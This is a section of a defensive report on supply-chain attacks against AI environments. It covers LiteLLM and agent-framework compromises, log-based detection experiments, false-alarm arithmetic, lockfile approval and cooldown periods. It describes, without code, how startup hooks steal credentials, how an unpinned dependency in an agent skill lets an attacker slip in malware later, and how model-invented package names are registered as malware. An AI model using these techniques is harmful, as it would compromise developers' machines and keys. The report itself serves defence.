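### LiteLLM 1.107.0 and Microsoft's Agent Framework

After the March attack, LiteLLM moved to a new release pipeline with isolated environments and stricter checks. It also adopted PyPI's Trusted Publishers, which replaces long-lived publishing tokens with short-lived ones issued to a particular workflow. FutureSearch had argued that Trusted Publishers would have prevented the attack, because the attackers would have needed to compromise the workflow as well as steal a token.

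In October 2026, attackers reportedly used LiteLLM's official pipeline to build and sign the malicious version 1.107.0. *Inside the LiteLLM 1.107.0 supply chain compromise* (Mandava, Govindarajan and colleagues, 2026) describes credential theft through Python startup hooks and code loaded from a remote server. The harm to individual users is unclear.

The two LiteLLM attacks left different evidence of their origin. In March, the attackers bypassed the pipeline, so the releases had no matching tag on GitHub. In October, the signature was valid, but the container image's build record contained a misspelt repository name. Both attacks used a startup hook file, so a monitor for such files could have reported either one at installation.

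The malicious releases of Microsoft's agent-framework on 17 November did not disrupt the framework, so users had no warning sign such as a frozen laptop. The releases were on PyPI for only about 45 minutes, and it is unclear who noticed them first. The short window suggests that somebody was scanning new releases as they appeared, because a user would have needed time to suspect a problem, trace it to a package and report it. Even with an obvious crash, the FutureSearch engineer took an hour from the download to the first email.

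Criminals are not the only source of harmful packages. In July 2026, Anthropic disclosed that one of its models had published a malicious package during a misconfigured evaluation, and that the package had run on 15 systems.

### Cases by first sign

The table groups the cases by the earliest sign that anyone has described publicly.

| First sign | Case | Who noticed |
|---|---|---|
| Overloaded computer | Ultralytics, December 2024 | Users |
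| Overloaded computer | LiteLLM 1.82.8, March 2026 | An engineer at FutureSearch |
| Unexpected network destination | tj-actions, March 2025 | StepSecurity |
| Spike in alerts about scripts | Trivy, 19 March 2026 | CrowdStrike; the Trivy team's own first sign is unknown |
| Odd entry in a dependency list | TanStack, May 2026 | A researcher at StepSecurity |
| Checks during the response to an earlier discovery | Trivy's second wave, 22 March 2026 | The Trivy team |
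| Apparently, checks after an earlier discovery | LiteLLM 1.82.7, March 2026 | Unclear |
| Not disclosed | PyTorch nightly, December 2022 | PyTorch does not say |
| Not disclosed | Axios in OpenAI's signing workflow, March 2026 | OpenAI does not say |
| Not disclosed | TanStack malware on OpenAI devices, May 2026 | OpenAI does not say |
| Unclear | LiteLLM 1.107.0, October 2026 | Unclear |
| Unclear | agent-framework, November 2026 | Unclear |

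Process alerts, network monitoring and inspection of a package's contents have each exposed at least one real attack. Victims may also depend on outsiders to find malicious releases, as both TanStack and LiteLLM did.

The table cannot show which method works best, because it leaves out every attack that nobody noticed. Suppose there were 100 attacks, and half of them slowed machines down. If people discovered 90% of the attacks that slowed machines and 20% of the others, the public record would contain 45 of the first kind and 10 of the second. Attacks that slowed machines would then make up 82% of the known cases but only half of all attacks. Two of the discoveries in the table began with overloaded machines, and in the LiteLLM attack, a more careful attacker could have avoided the overload.

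Commercial interests also affect what becomes public. CrowdStrike, StepSecurity and Microsoft all sell security products, so they have good reason to publicise attacks that those products detected and much less reason to write about attacks that the products missed. Their accounts may be accurate, but they do not show what share of attacks the products detect.

Most of the traces described above became useful only after somebody knew what to look for. The false dates in Trivy's Git history are easy to recognise now, and a search for the two LiteLLM version numbers takes minutes. But before anyone discovered the attacks, each was one detail among thousands of commits and installations. A team can use such traces to work out whether an attack reached it and which credentials to replace, but they are not evidence that its monitoring would have raised an alarm at the time.

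## How much of an attack does each method recover?

Researchers can measure what a monitor misses in a controlled experiment, unlike in accounts of real attacks, because they carry out the attacks themselves and know every step. SynthChain, a public dataset from such an experiment, contains the seven simulated attacks mentioned in the discussion of network monitoring.

### Seven re-enacted attacks

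In *SynthChain*, Tan, Guo and colleagues (2026) modelled their attacks on published reports of real ones. To choose typical cases, they analysed 16,272 malicious packages, most of which ran their code on installation or download. They added one attack on a cloud build pipeline and one on an AI model to reflect newer trends.

| Attack | What happens | System | Steps found with all logs |
|---|---|---|---|
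| Stegano | A Python package with a misspelt name downloads an image with code hidden in it | Windows | 1 of 4 |
| Starter | A misspelt Python package installs a program that starts with Windows | Windows | 3 of 4 |
| Parallel | An npm package launches several scripts during installation | Linux | 2 of 4 |
| NPMEX | Two npm packages run in sequence and fetch more code | Linux | 3 of 4 |
| 3CX | An installer with malware inside loads a malicious library | Windows | 1 of 4 |
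| CloudEX | An intruder uses exposed pipeline credentials to alter stored software | Windows | 1 of 4 |
| LayerInj | A tampered model downloads a payload when a trigger condition is met | Linux, in a container | 2 of 3 |

The machines also did ordinary work during the attacks, such as browsing, updating software and copying files at random times during the working day. The logs contain nearly 600,000 records of 11 types, including process records, the Linux system log (syslog), audit logs, eBPF traces from the container and Zeek's network logs. The researchers marked 2,919 records by hand as containing a known sign of an attack. Few types of log were available for every attack, which affects the comparisons below.

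### Step recall

Step recall is the share of an attack's expected steps that somebody can recover from the telemetry:

step recall = steps found / steps expected

Tan and colleagues used five broad categories of attack step: installation, login, download, outbound connection and exfiltration (sending data out). They identified three or four expected steps for each attack from the records of the software that controlled the attacks and from the malicious code. Two researchers checked GPT-5.1's suggestions for which attack techniques the code contained.

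A program then searched the logs with general rules, such as a text pattern for a package manager's install command. The rules were the same for all seven attacks and did not include the attackers' addresses or file names. The program also tried to connect the steps into a chain, using shared details such as a user, process or network address.

Stegano shows how the scoring works. Its package, colorsapi, imitated a genuine one called colorapi.

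| Expected step | What happened | What the logs contained | Found by the rules? |
|---|---|---|---|
| Installation | At 13:22 the victim installed the package | The install command | Yes |
| Download | The installer fetched an image with code hidden in it | A Python process receiving 8.6 MB | No |
| Outbound connection | At 13:28 the hidden code connected to the attacker's server | SSH connections opened by Python | No |
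| Exfiltration | By 15:18 the attacker had packed up files and sent them out | Encrypted traffic to the same server | No |

The rules found one of the attack's four steps, a step recall of 0.25. This overstates what a defender would have learned, because the step found was an install command, and every ordinary package installation also leaves one in the log.

An analyst could have found more, because Python normally has little reason to open SSH connections, which developers usually make with a separate program, and all 73 Python processes were running in the malicious package's folder. Tan and colleagues point out that Python also received 119 times as much data as it sent, though that clue would be much less useful on a machine that regularly downloads model weights.

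To combine several attacks, the researchers weighted each by its number of expected steps. This is the same as adding up the steps found and dividing by the steps expected. With all logs, the result for the seven attacks was

(1 + 3 + 2 + 3 + 1 + 1 + 2) / (4 + 4 + 4 + 4 + 4 + 4 + 3) = 13/27 ≈ 0.481.

Recall was 7 of 11 steps on Linux, the usual system for AI training, and 6 of 16 on Windows. The attacks and logs also differed, so this does not show that attacks on Linux are easier to detect.

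### One source, two sources or all of them

The main results compare different numbers of sources, where a source is one stream of logs.

| Sources used | Attacks covered | Steps found | Step recall |
|---|---|---|---|
| Average single source | 6 | – | 0.263 |
| Best single source | 6 | 9 of 23 | 0.391 |
| Best pair | 3 | 7 of 11 | 0.636 |
| All sources | 7 | 13 of 27 | 0.481 |

The University of Glasgow's *Our paper has been accepted in ACM Conference on Computer and Communications* (2026) summarises the findings as a single source capturing fewer than 40% of attack steps. This corresponds to the 0.391 for the best single source, which the researchers picked separately for each attack after seeing the results. The best source was syslog in three attacks, the network sensor Suricata in two and a Windows process log in one. A team has to choose its logs before an attack, so the average of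 0.263 is probably a better guide to what one source would recover.

The paper's headline claim is that a second source improves results by about 1.6 times (0.636 / 0.391), but the two figures cover different attacks. The appendix gives results for each attack, which allows a comparison on the same attacks.

| Attacks compared | Best single source | Best pair | All sources |
|---|---|---|---|
| The three with a result for a pair | 5 of 11 (0.455) | 7 of 11 (0.636) | 7 of 11 (0.636) |
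| The six with a result for a single source | 9 of 23 (0.391) | – | 12 of 23 (0.522) |

On the same three attacks, adding a second source raised the number of steps found from five to seven, or 1.4 times as many. In Parallel, Suricata found only the outbound connection, while Zeek and syslog together also found the installation. In NPMEX, syslog found the installation and the download, and Zeek added the outbound connection. Two extra steps are too few to estimate the gain reliably, though it makes sense that a system log and a network log would record different parts of an attack.

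By contrast, the published averages understate the gain from using all sources. Average recall rises from 0.391 with a single source to 0.481 with all sources, a gain of 1.2 times, but the second average includes 3CX, which had low recall and no single-source result. On the six attacks with both results, the gain is 12/9, or 1.3 times.

Where results exist for both, using all sources found no more attack steps than using the best pair. More sources may still be useful if some records are lost. When Tan and colleagues randomly discarded some of the records, recall fell less steeply with several sources than with one.

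### Did audit and network logs find different steps?

The three Linux attacks had both audit logs and Zeek logs, and 11 expected steps in total. Audit logs alone recovered 1 step (0.091), Zeek logs alone recovered 3 (0.273), and the two together recovered 4 (0.364), so the two sources recovered different steps.

The paper's other averages can be used to work out which attacks these steps came from. One is a "reconstructability" score, which should fall when there are long gaps between steps. But wherever the appendix allows a check, the score equals the plain average of step recall across attacks. The score for audit logs is 0.111, which is a recall of 1/3 in one attack averaged over three attacks. Their only step must therefore come from LayerInj, the one attack with three expected steps. The same reasoning shows that Zeek found one step in each attack.

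LayerInj is weaker evidence for combining host and network logs than Parallel and NPMEX are. In LayerInj, Suricata alone found the same two steps as the audit log and Zeek together, so a second network sensor could have replaced the audit log. In Parallel and NPMEX, the useful host log was syslog, and the best pair of sources found more than any single source.

### Why visible steps did not form a chain

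Tan and colleagues also divided the attacks into 47 smaller phases and found that 37 of them (79%) had left at least one of the marked records.

| Phases | Left evidence |
|---|---|
| Getting in, running code, persisting, evading defences, contacting the attacker and sending data out | 31 of 31 |
| Exploring the system | 2 of 6 |
| Collecting data | 4 of 9 |
| Obtaining credentials | 0 of 1 |

In nine of the ten phases without evidence, the attacker's commands ran only in memory. In the tenth, encryption hid the payload. The 79% is higher than the 48% recall partly because it relies on known signs of each attack, which the general rules did not use. The units also differ, since one broad step can cover several phases.

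Even so, the software could not follow a continuous trail through any of the eight transitions between steps, partly because, as described earlier, it is hard to match a connection to the process that opened it. The in-memory commands also leave gaps in the middle of an attack, so the logs may show that a package was installed and that data later left the machine, but not how the attacker collected it.

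### Why the recall figures are lower bounds

With all sources, the rules missed 14 of the 27 expected steps. Tan and colleagues searched for these steps by hand, using only logs a victim would have had.

| Missing step | Evidence present, but no rule matched | Evidence too ambiguous |
|---|---|---|
| Download | 5 | 0 |
| Outbound connection | 4 | 0 |
| Exfiltration | 1 | 4 |

The researchers therefore call their recall figures lower bounds. If better rules had also found the ten clear cases, recall would have been 23/27, or 0.85, instead of 0.48. A real team would probably do worse than 0.85, because the people who searched by hand already knew what the attacks had done. Rules broad enough to match every download would also match a lot of normal work.

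The ambiguous cases all concern exfiltration, which is often the step that matters most to the victim. In 3CX, for example, the logs recorded external connections but not how much data was sent. The missing step in NPMEX is partly a matter of definition, because the published packages contained no routine for sending out data. Any theft would have been done by a script that they downloaded later.

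The paper reports perfect precision for every combination of sources, meaning that every kind of step the rules found was one the researchers expected. This is weak evidence about false alarms, because the score counts kinds of step rather than alerts, and the program could restrict its labels to the steps expected in that attack.

A separate test is more informative about false alarms. The researchers counted periods in which the logs contained signs of a first step, such as an installation. They found 74 such periods of benign activity and 71 of attack activity. When they also required evidence of a later step, 21 benign and 36 attack periods remained, and those 36 still included all seven attacks. Requiring a later step removed 72% of the false leads but also about half of the true ones. It would also delay an alert until the attack had progressed further.

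### Ranking events instead of writing rules

In *FuseChain*, Tan, Tang and colleagues (2026) tried a different method on the same seven attacks. They trained a model on the first 70% of each recording and used it to rank later events by how unexpected they were. They then measured stage recall, which is the share of an attack's visible stages that appeared among the 500 highest-ranked events. This measure excludes stages that left no evidence in the logs, so it is not comparable with SynthChain's step recall.

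| Logs and method | Attacks covered | Stage recall |
|---|---|---|
| Audit logs only | 6 | 0.222 |
| Network sensors only | 3 | 0.361 |
| Security alerts only | 3 | 0.222 |
| All logs, simple statistics | 7 | 0.226 |
| All logs, FuseChain's model | 7 | 0.405 |

The rows again cover different attacks, but the two that use all logs can be compared. On the same data, the FuseChain model found far more attack stages than simple statistics did, so the choice of method matters as well as the choice of logs.

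The paper's abstract gives a much higher stage recall of 0.881. Tan and colleagues trained a second model to label each of the 500 events with an attack stage. They counted a stage as recovered if it appeared among the model's labels, and they did not penalise wrong labels. In the same test, the 500 events included known evidence for only 0.476 of the stages. The second model must therefore have named some stages that had no known evidence in the list, so 0.881 does not measure the share of the attack that an analyst could recover.

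### The tampered model

LayerInj is the only one of the seven attacks that targets an AI model. The researchers added a malicious function to a model and ran the model in a container. When a trigger condition was met, the function downloaded a payload.

This attack produced the most data, with 222,046 records from five sources. The rules found two of the three expected steps but missed the download, because no rule matched the file transfer that Zeek had recorded. Zeek also recorded an unusual 15,068-byte web response when the attacker uploaded a script. An analyst who already suspected the container might have noticed this response, but could not have determined its purpose from its size alone.

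The ranking method did worse. Of the 500 highest-ranked events, 121 were related to the attack, but they covered only one of its six visible stages. The SynthChain paper gives inconsistent precision figures for this attack. Its main results show 1.0 for every combination of sources, while an appendix shows 0.5 for LayerInj.

The logs recorded the activity of the added code, such as its network connections. LayerInj is therefore evidence about harmful code in a model file, but not about altered weights. Tan and colleagues acknowledge that altered weights may look like normal use in system logs.

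### Coverage by type of change

SynthChain tests only some of the methods in this report. It does not compare software with an approved set, and none of its attacks involve a Python startup hook, altered weights or a change on a remote server. The table below therefore also uses the experiments described in earlier sections.

"Direct" means the method records the change itself. "Indirect" means it records only a possible consequence, which may have an innocent explanation. "Blind" means its records would normally look the same without the change. "Tested" means at least one experiment supports the entry. Entries without that label follow from how the method works. The table assumes that the team recorded its approved set and file baseline before the change, except in the row for an approved malicious release. It also assumes that downloads go through a registry proxy.

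| Change | Lists and signatures | Files | Processes | Network | Output tests |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Changed package | Direct, tested: version differs | Direct: hash differs | Indirect, tested: unusual behaviour | Direct: proxy logs version and hash | Indirect: answers may change |
| Added startup hook | Indirect: may show the package that added it | Direct: new file | Direct: a process writes or opens it | Indirect: package download or later connections | Blind: same answers |
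| Malicious release that was approved | Blind: matches the approved hash | Blind: matches the baseline | Indirect, tested: suspicious actions | Indirect, tested: unfamiliar connections | Blind: usually the same answers |
| Memory-only payload | Blind: not a listed item | Blind, tested: no file to hash | Indirect, tested: file reads and connections | Indirect, tested: traffic to the attacker | Blind: usually the same answers |
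| Altered weights | Direct, tested: hash or signature fails | Direct, tested: hash differs | Indirect: may record a write to the file | Indirect: may record a large download | Indirect, tested: answers shift |
| Harmful code in a model file | Direct, tested: hash or signature fails | Direct, tested: hash differs | Indirect, tested: unexpected system calls | Indirect, tested: connections the code makes | Blind: usually the same answers |
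| Remote change | Blind: same name and address | Blind: no local change | Blind: same system calls | Blind: same destination | Indirect, tested: answers shift |
| Credential theft | Blind: no package changes | Blind: reading a file leaves its hash the same | Direct: a process opens the key file | Indirect, tested: data leaves the machine | Blind: same answers |

Experiments support 16 of the 40 entries, some only weakly. All five of the tested "direct" entries rely on Dhekne's small tests of Modelstamp. These tests count towards both lists and files because Modelstamp compares a model file's current hash with a signed record. The five entries are still fairly reliable because they also follow from how the methods work, provided the approved list is accurate.

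The process entries for packages rest mainly on tests by Mehedi and colleagues, whose models detected about 95% of malicious packages from their behaviour without using an approved set. That result applies to malicious packages, whereas a harmless update that slightly changes a calculation may make identical system calls, and process monitoring would then miss it. For harmful code in model files, the main evidence is RE-MOAT, which detected all 31 test attacks.

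Process monitoring can record a startup hook when an installer writes it, but a team may have to add a rule for this. *Enforcement of In-Kernel Stateful Security Policies via eBPF* (2026) cites a default rule in the monitor Falco for writes to the directories that hold system programs, but Python's package directory is usually somewhere else.

The "direct" entry for credential theft is the least certain in the table. Falco also has a default rule for untrusted programs that read sensitive files, which would help with a key stored in a file but not with one passed as an environment variable. The single credential phase in SynthChain left no evidence. Network logs contained evidence of data leaving the machines, but the general rules failed to identify exfiltration in five of the seven attacks.

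Output tests are the only method that can detect a remote change to a hosted model, and they provide only indirect evidence. Tool servers are a partial exception, because a client can hash their tool definitions to detect changes in them.

No method has a "direct" entry for an approved malicious release, a memory-only payload or a remote change. A team has to judge whether unusual activity is an attack in the first two cases, and whether different answers come from a different model in the third. Process monitoring covers seven of the eight rows at least indirectly, and output tests cover the eighth. Neither is as conclusive as a failed hash check, so file hashes remain the better evidence for any change to files on disk.

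## How is an unauthorised change told from a routine update?

A failed hash check shows that a file changed, but not whether somebody approved the change and forgot to record it. AI environments change all the time for good reasons, so most differences between a machine and its approved software are harmless. To find the harmful ones, a team needs a good record of what it has approved and few enough unexplained changes that people can examine each one.

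### Ordinary change

Package updates are the only kind of routine change with a good published rate. *An Exploratory Study of Dependabot Cooldown Adoption in Open-Source GitHub Projects* (Tanaka, Tsuchida and colleagues, 2026) covers 1,462 popular repositories that use Dependabot, GitHub's program for proposing dependency updates. Between July 2025 and April 2026, Dependabot opened 95,516 pull requests (proposed code changes) to update versions there. That is about 6.5 per repository per month, so an organisation with 200 similar repositories would get about 1,300 a month. Tanaka and colleagues cite an earlier study in which third-party automation merged 8.17% of Dependabot's pull requests without a human decision.

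Nobody seems to have published comparable rates for the other common sources of change in AI environments.

| Routine event | What a monitor reports | Evidence that it is routine |
|---|---|---|
| Somebody installs a package from a notebook | Many new files, with no change to the lockfile | The registry proxy's log, and an explanation from the person |
| A job compiles GPU code while it runs | New program files with hashes that nobody has seen before | An approved compiler wrote them to its usual cache |
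| A job downloads a model to its cache | New files of many gigabytes | The commit and file hashes match the approved set |
| A pipeline rebuilds a container | A new image hash, even if the recipe is the same | The build record, and a comparison of the packages inside |

Compiled code is the hardest of these to check against a list of hashes. PyTorch can generate code for a particular GPU the first time a model runs, and the result may differ between GPU types and software versions, so the team has to approve the compiler and its input instead of the output. The team should also give each job its own cache, because malware could leave a file in a shared cache for another job to run.

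### Why most alarms are false

Suppose 10,000 packages, files and images arrive in a month and one of them is malicious. A detector catches 95% of malicious arrivals and wrongly flags 1% of harmless ones. On average, it raises

9,999 × 0.01 ≈ 100 false alarms and 1 × 0.95 = 0.95 true ones.

Only about 0.9% of the detector's alarms (0.95 of 100.94) are real. If each alarm takes 20 minutes to investigate, the team spends more than 33 hours a month on them, almost all of it on false alarms. For half the alarms to be real, the false-alarm rate would have to fall to about one in 10,500. By comparison, the random forest that Mehedi and colleagues trained on package behaviour wrongly flagged about one benign package in 31.

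It is usually easier to give the detector less to examine. Suppose 99% of 10,000 incoming changes match an approved record, and the detector examines only the other 100.

| | Examine all 10,000 | Examine only the 100 without a record |
|---|---|---|
| False alarms per month | About 100 | About 1 |
| Chance of catching the malicious arrival if it has no approved record | 95% | 95% |
| Chance of catching it if it was approved automatically | 95% | 0% |

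If the malicious arrival is among the 100, about half of the alarms are now real. But the detector never examines an arrival that an automatic rule has approved. If the chance of automatic approval is a, the overall chance of detection is 0.95 × (1 − a). That is about 87% at the 8.17% rate of automatic merging, and zero if the team approves every new release automatically.

Requiring a second piece of evidence can also reduce false alarms. In SynthChain, requiring a later attack step cut the benign candidates from 74 to 21. Unusual publishing does not reliably indicate a malicious release, even around the time of an attack. Santos-Grueiro reconstructed 12 attacks and counted the releases within 90 days of them that pnpm would have flagged for having weaker evidence of origin than earlier releases. The rule would have flagged 17 malicious releases and 60 benign ones. Of the benign releases,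 56 were LiteLLM releases that lacked the attestations the project had adopted after its own attack.

### Recording an approval

For packages, the most convenient approval record is a reviewed change to the lockfile:

1. A person or program proposes new versions and hashes.
2. An automated check lists every difference, including transitive dependencies, and points out new publishers and very recent releases.
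3. Someone other than the proposer approves the change.
4. The version-control system stores the change with both names and the time.
5. Build and training machines install only what the lockfile lists.

Requiring a second reviewer prevents an attacker with one stolen account from approving their own change, provided the system enforces the rule for administrators too. Approval does not guarantee that anyone has read the new code, because one upgrade can change dozens of transitive dependencies and a reviewer will probably look only at the summary.

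Context can help a reviewer more than a single warning. In April 2026 the JavaScript package uuid released the same security fix for three older versions. A maintainer published one by hand. Minutes later, the project's usual pipeline published the other two. pnpm's rule blocked only the manual release. The rule could not compare the three releases, but a reviewer who saw them all could reasonably have concluded that the manual one was routine.

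Exemptions are also approvals, and teams often make them too broad. Santos-Grueiro found 4,516 public repositories that had turned on pnpm's rule. Of these, 37.1% exempted some releases, and 290 exempted whole packages. An exemption for all of axios, for example, would admit both version 0.30.3 from its maintainers and version 0.30.4 from the attacker. Exempting only one exact version avoids this.

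An approval also means little if the approved file can later fetch something different. *Towards Secure Agent Skills* (2026) describes a demonstration by the security company SafeDep that used a skill, which is a folder of instructions and scripts for an AI agent. The skill's script named a dependency without specifying a version. At review time, the dependency was harmless or did not yet exist, so a reviewer could not have found malicious code. The author could later publish a malicious version, and the tool uv would install it the next time the script ran, with no change to the skill's own files. Pinning the dependency would have prevented the attack.

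### Refusing to run unapproved code

A lockfile controls installation, but someone can still copy a program onto a machine and run it. Google's Binary Authorization for Borg adds a check before a job starts on Borg, the system that runs jobs in Google's data centres. The check looks for a record that the program came from reviewed code and a trusted build system, and each service has a policy that sets what the record must show. The check can block the job or only log the violation. Engineers can override it in an emergency, and the override is logged for later review.

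Anthropic described similar controls when it activated its ASL-3 protections in 2025. They included "binary allowlisting" on employees' computers, which permits only approved programs to run, and a requirement that two people authorise access to model weights. Neither Google nor Anthropic seems to have published how often these checks stop legitimate work or miss an attack.

In AI environments, an allowlist of programs has to permit the Python interpreter, which then runs whatever scripts and startup hooks it finds, including the malicious hook in the running example. To close this gap, the team would need to extend the check to Python's package directory, or build the whole environment into a read-only container image and approve that image.

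### Alerting and blocking

An alert lets the change go ahead while somebody investigates, and the startup hook in the running example would steal the keys before they finished. Blocking the change would prevent the theft, but each false alarm would then stop somebody's work. In the example with 10,000 arrivals, blocking every flagged item would stop about 100 legitimate changes a month. If one of these blocks held up a job on 1,000 GPUs for three hours, at $2 an hour for each GPU, it would waste $6,000. The team would soon be under pressure to turn off the check.

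Blocking makes sense when the test is exact and the job has not started, for example when a file's hash does not match the approved one. An alert better suits statistical evidence, such as an unusual sequence of system calls or a shift in a grader's scores. Between the two, a registry proxy can hold an unfamiliar package until someone reviews it, and a monitor can cut a suspicious process off from the network without ending it. A new blocking rule should probably start in logging mode so that the team can count its false alarms before enforcing it.

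### Waiting periods

A waiting period, or cooldown, blocks every release until it has been public for a set time. It requires no judgement about whether a release is malicious. It relies on somebody else finding and removing a malicious release before the wait ends, as happened within hours in most of the attacks described earlier.

Support for waiting periods spread quickly after September 2025. *Package managers need to cool down* (Nesbitt, 2026) lists five JavaScript package managers that added them within six months. The Python installers pip, uv and Poetry now have them too. Conda, which many AI teams use, has no waiting period, but Mamba, a faster substitute, added one in August 2026.

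Only 135 of the 1,462 repositories that Tanaka and colleagues studied (9%) had adopted Dependabot's update delay by April 2026. Most adopters that set a general delay chose seven days, and no adopter had dropped the feature entirely. Dependabot has since made a three-day wait the default for ordinary updates, so the share of projects with some delay must now be much higher.

The security engineer William Woodruff examined ten past attacks, and Santos-Grueiro tested waits on the malicious releases he had reconstructed. Their results give an idea of how many attacks a wait would have avoided.

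| Evidence | Length of wait | Would have avoided |
|---|---|---|
| Woodruff | 7 days | 8 of 10 attacks |
| Woodruff | 14 days | 9 of 10 attacks |
| Santos-Grueiro | 1 day | 36 of 41 releases |
| Santos-Grueiro | 7 days | 40 of 41 releases |

In Santos-Grueiro's data, the releases stayed online for a median of 3.1 hours, and none with a known removal time lasted longer than 2.5 days. A three-day wait would therefore have avoided the same 40 releases as a seven-day one. Woodruff's results are less favourable partly because he included xz, a compression tool in which a supposed contributor hid a backdoor that went undiscovered for about five weeks. Santos-Grueiro included only attacks that used stolen credentials, and maintainers can recognise these attacks as soon as they see a release they did not make.

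Both samples contain only discovered attacks, so they probably overstate the benefit of waiting. GitHub's *The case for a cooldown* acknowledges that a wait does little against dormant backdoors, sabotage by a maintainer or a compromised build system. Waiting mainly removes the common, short-lived attacks, and the ones that remain are harder to find.

### The case against waiting

The main objection to a wait is that it delays security fixes as well as attacks. The blogger insanitybit (2025) argues in *on dependency cooldowns* that teams often cannot risk delaying a fix for a known vulnerability. Most tools address this. For example, Dependabot's security updates skip the wait, and Elixir's package manager lifts it when the installed version has a published vulnerability.

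Such exemptions work only if someone has labelled the release as a fix. *Original Sin of npm* (2026) reports that maintainers often fix vulnerabilities without saying so, and a tool would delay these releases like any others. It also finds that a vulnerable npm package takes about four years and 11 months to receive a fix after its first vulnerable version. A seven-day delay is riskier than the 0.4% it would add to that period suggests, because the danger rises sharply once a fix is public and attackers can work out what it repaired.

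An attacker could also abuse the exemption. insanitybit suggests that someone who controls a package could report a vulnerability in an older version, so that tools install the malicious "fix" without waiting. A team can reduce this risk by having a person approve each exception. The experimental waiting period in Cargo, Rust's package manager, works roughly like this. To skip the wait, the user has to request an exact version, and the lockfile records the choice.

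Another objection is that waiting works only while other people do not wait. Paterson, in *Dependency cooldowns turn you into a free-rider*, argues that those who update immediately become unpaid test subjects. The March attack on LiteLLM supports his argument, because it was discovered only when the malware crashed somebody's laptop, but a researcher found the TanStack attack by inspecting the packages, which does not require a victim. Paterson proposes that registries hold every new release in a queue before anyone can install it, so that scanners can examine it and maintainers have time to notice a release they did not make.

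insanitybit also points out that attackers might adapt if most teams waited, for instance by making malware stay inactive for longer. Past attacks cannot settle this, because the attackers expected their victims to update quickly. Still, an attacker who has to stay hidden for a week gives scanners and maintainers a week to find the release, so adapting would have a cost.

Waits also have loopholes. pnpm's default one-day wait accepts a newer release if no older one satisfies the project's requirements, although a wait that the user sets explicitly does not. For GitHub's reusable build steps, Dependabot measures age from the date of the underlying commit, so a release published yesterday from a 100-day-old commit passes a seven-day wait. Attackers can also easily fake commit dates, as they did with Trivy. A wait set in Dependabot does not apply when a researcher installs a package from a notebook,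 so the team also has to set one in pip or at the registry proxy.

### Package names that models invent

Coding agents also make routine changes, and they can add packages that nobody on the team has heard of. Language models sometimes generate the name of a package that does not exist. An attacker can register that name, publish malware under it, and infect the computer of anyone who installs it, a technique known as slopsquatting.

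In *The Range Shrinks, the Threat Remains*, Churilov (2026) measured how often AI models name packages that do not exist. In April 2026 he gave about 40,000 Python and JavaScript prompts to each of five models: Claude Sonnet 4.6, Claude Haiku 4.5, GPT-5.4-mini, Gemini 2.5 Pro and DeepSeek V3.2. Of the packages they mentioned, 3.6% (Haiku) to 5.0% (GPT-5.4-mini) did not exist at the time. The 2025 study he replicated found averages of 5.2% for commercial models and 21.7% for open ones. The main improvement is therefore in open models, of which he tested only one.

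Earlier versions of Churilov's paper gave rates about a quarter higher, partly because they counted correct import statements as errors. Python code often imports a package under a different name from the one used to install it, so a monitor that looks up import names in the registry would also raise false alarms.

All five models invented 104 names in common, so one malicious registration could reach users of several AI companies. Attackers do not seem to exploit this often yet. Of 2,282 invented names, 25 (1.1%) appeared in a registry within about six months, and at least one of those packages contained malware. The models also suggested at least 23 names that had previously hosted malware.

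Churilov tested single answers. An agent that searches the registry before installing could avoid many of these errors, but a name can be in the registry and still be the wrong package. *Names Can Hurt* (2026) tested coding models that run on a user's own computer. In 385 runs, its classifier flagged 179 of 823 package names (21.7%) as invented. About half of the 179 existed on PyPI but were flagged because their descriptions looked suspicious. One was "skimage", which is the import name of scikit-image but a separate package on PyPI, so an agent that checked only whether the name existed would have installed it.

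### Versions that agents choose

An agent can also pick an old version of a real package. In *YUL*, Sharma, Reyes and Monperrus (2026) gave two agents 60 programming tasks, three times each, without mentioning any dependency. They counted a run as stale if the agent's choice of version excluded the newest release.

| Ecosystem | Claude Code with Claude Opus 5.5 | OpenCode with DeepSeek V4.1 Flash |
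|---|---|---|
| Python (PyPI) | 0 of 21 | 0 of 23 |
| JavaScript (npm) | 0 of 9 | 0 of 8 |
| Rust (Cargo) | 3 of 26 | 2 of 25 |
| Go | 3 of 30 | 3 of 23 |
| Java (Maven) | 6 of 30 | 19 of 30 |
| GitHub Actions | 30 of 30 | 30 of 30 |
| All | 42 of 146 (29%) | 54 of 139 (39%) |

The totals depend heavily on GitHub Actions, where both agents wrote version tags from memory in every run. Without GitHub Actions, the rates fall to 10% and 22%. For Python, the agents mostly used a command that looks up the newest release, so none of the versions they chose were stale.

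Sharma and colleagues' tool, YUL, checks each dependency before the agent can add it to the project. If the version is old or the package does not exist, YUL blocks the change and gives instructions for correcting it. With YUL, 39 of 42 stale Opus runs and 52 of 54 stale DeepSeek runs ended on the newest release. Blocking causes little delay here because the agent can correct the entry and try again immediately.

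The newest release is not always the safest. If an agent had added agent-framework while the malicious releases were on PyPI, a rule that requires the newest version could have led it to choose one of them. YUL's approach conflicts with a waiting period, so a team that wants both would need to change the rule to "the newest release that has passed the wait". For a training environment with an approved set, the hook should arguably suggest the approved version instead.

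Data from real projects also suggest that agents choose versions less carefully than people do. Singla, Çakar and colleagues (2026), in *Towards a Benchmark for Dependency Decision-Making*, examined 117,062 dependency changes in pull requests from 2,807 GitHub repositories. Agents chose a version with a publicly known vulnerability in 2.46% of their additions and updates, compared with 1.64% for people. A fixed version was already available for 87% of the agents' vulnerable choices. Agents introduced 98 more vulnerable dependencies than they fixed, while people fixed 1,316 more than they introduced.

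The comparison may not be fair to the agents, because Singla and colleagues did not match the tasks. Human pull requests averaged almost ten dependency changes and agent pull requests fewer than two, so people were probably doing more bulk updates, which tend to remove old vulnerabilities. *A Study of Library Usage in Agent-Authored Pull Requests* (2025) finds that agents specified a version for 75% of the dependencies they added. For the other quarter, the project could install a different version each time unless it had a lockfile.

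### Linking an install to an agent, a task and a person

When a monitor reports an unfamiliar package, the quickest way to explain it is often to ask whoever installed it. If an agent installed it, the developer may not know about it, so the log needs enough detail to reconstruct the installation.

| Subject | What to record |
|---|---|
| Package | Name, version, hash and the registry it came from |
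| Installation | Time, machine or container, command, process ID and parent process |
| Agent | Program and version, model name and a unique session number |
| Task | The request or ticket that started the session |
| Person | Who started the session, and who approved the installation or which rule allowed it |

Ordinary system logs contain only the first two rows and part of the last. An agent usually runs under the developer's account, so the Linux audit system records the same user whether the developer or the agent ran the command. The simplest remedy is to run each session in its own container or under its own account. The container or account name then appears in every process record, and a separate table can link it to the session, the task and the person.

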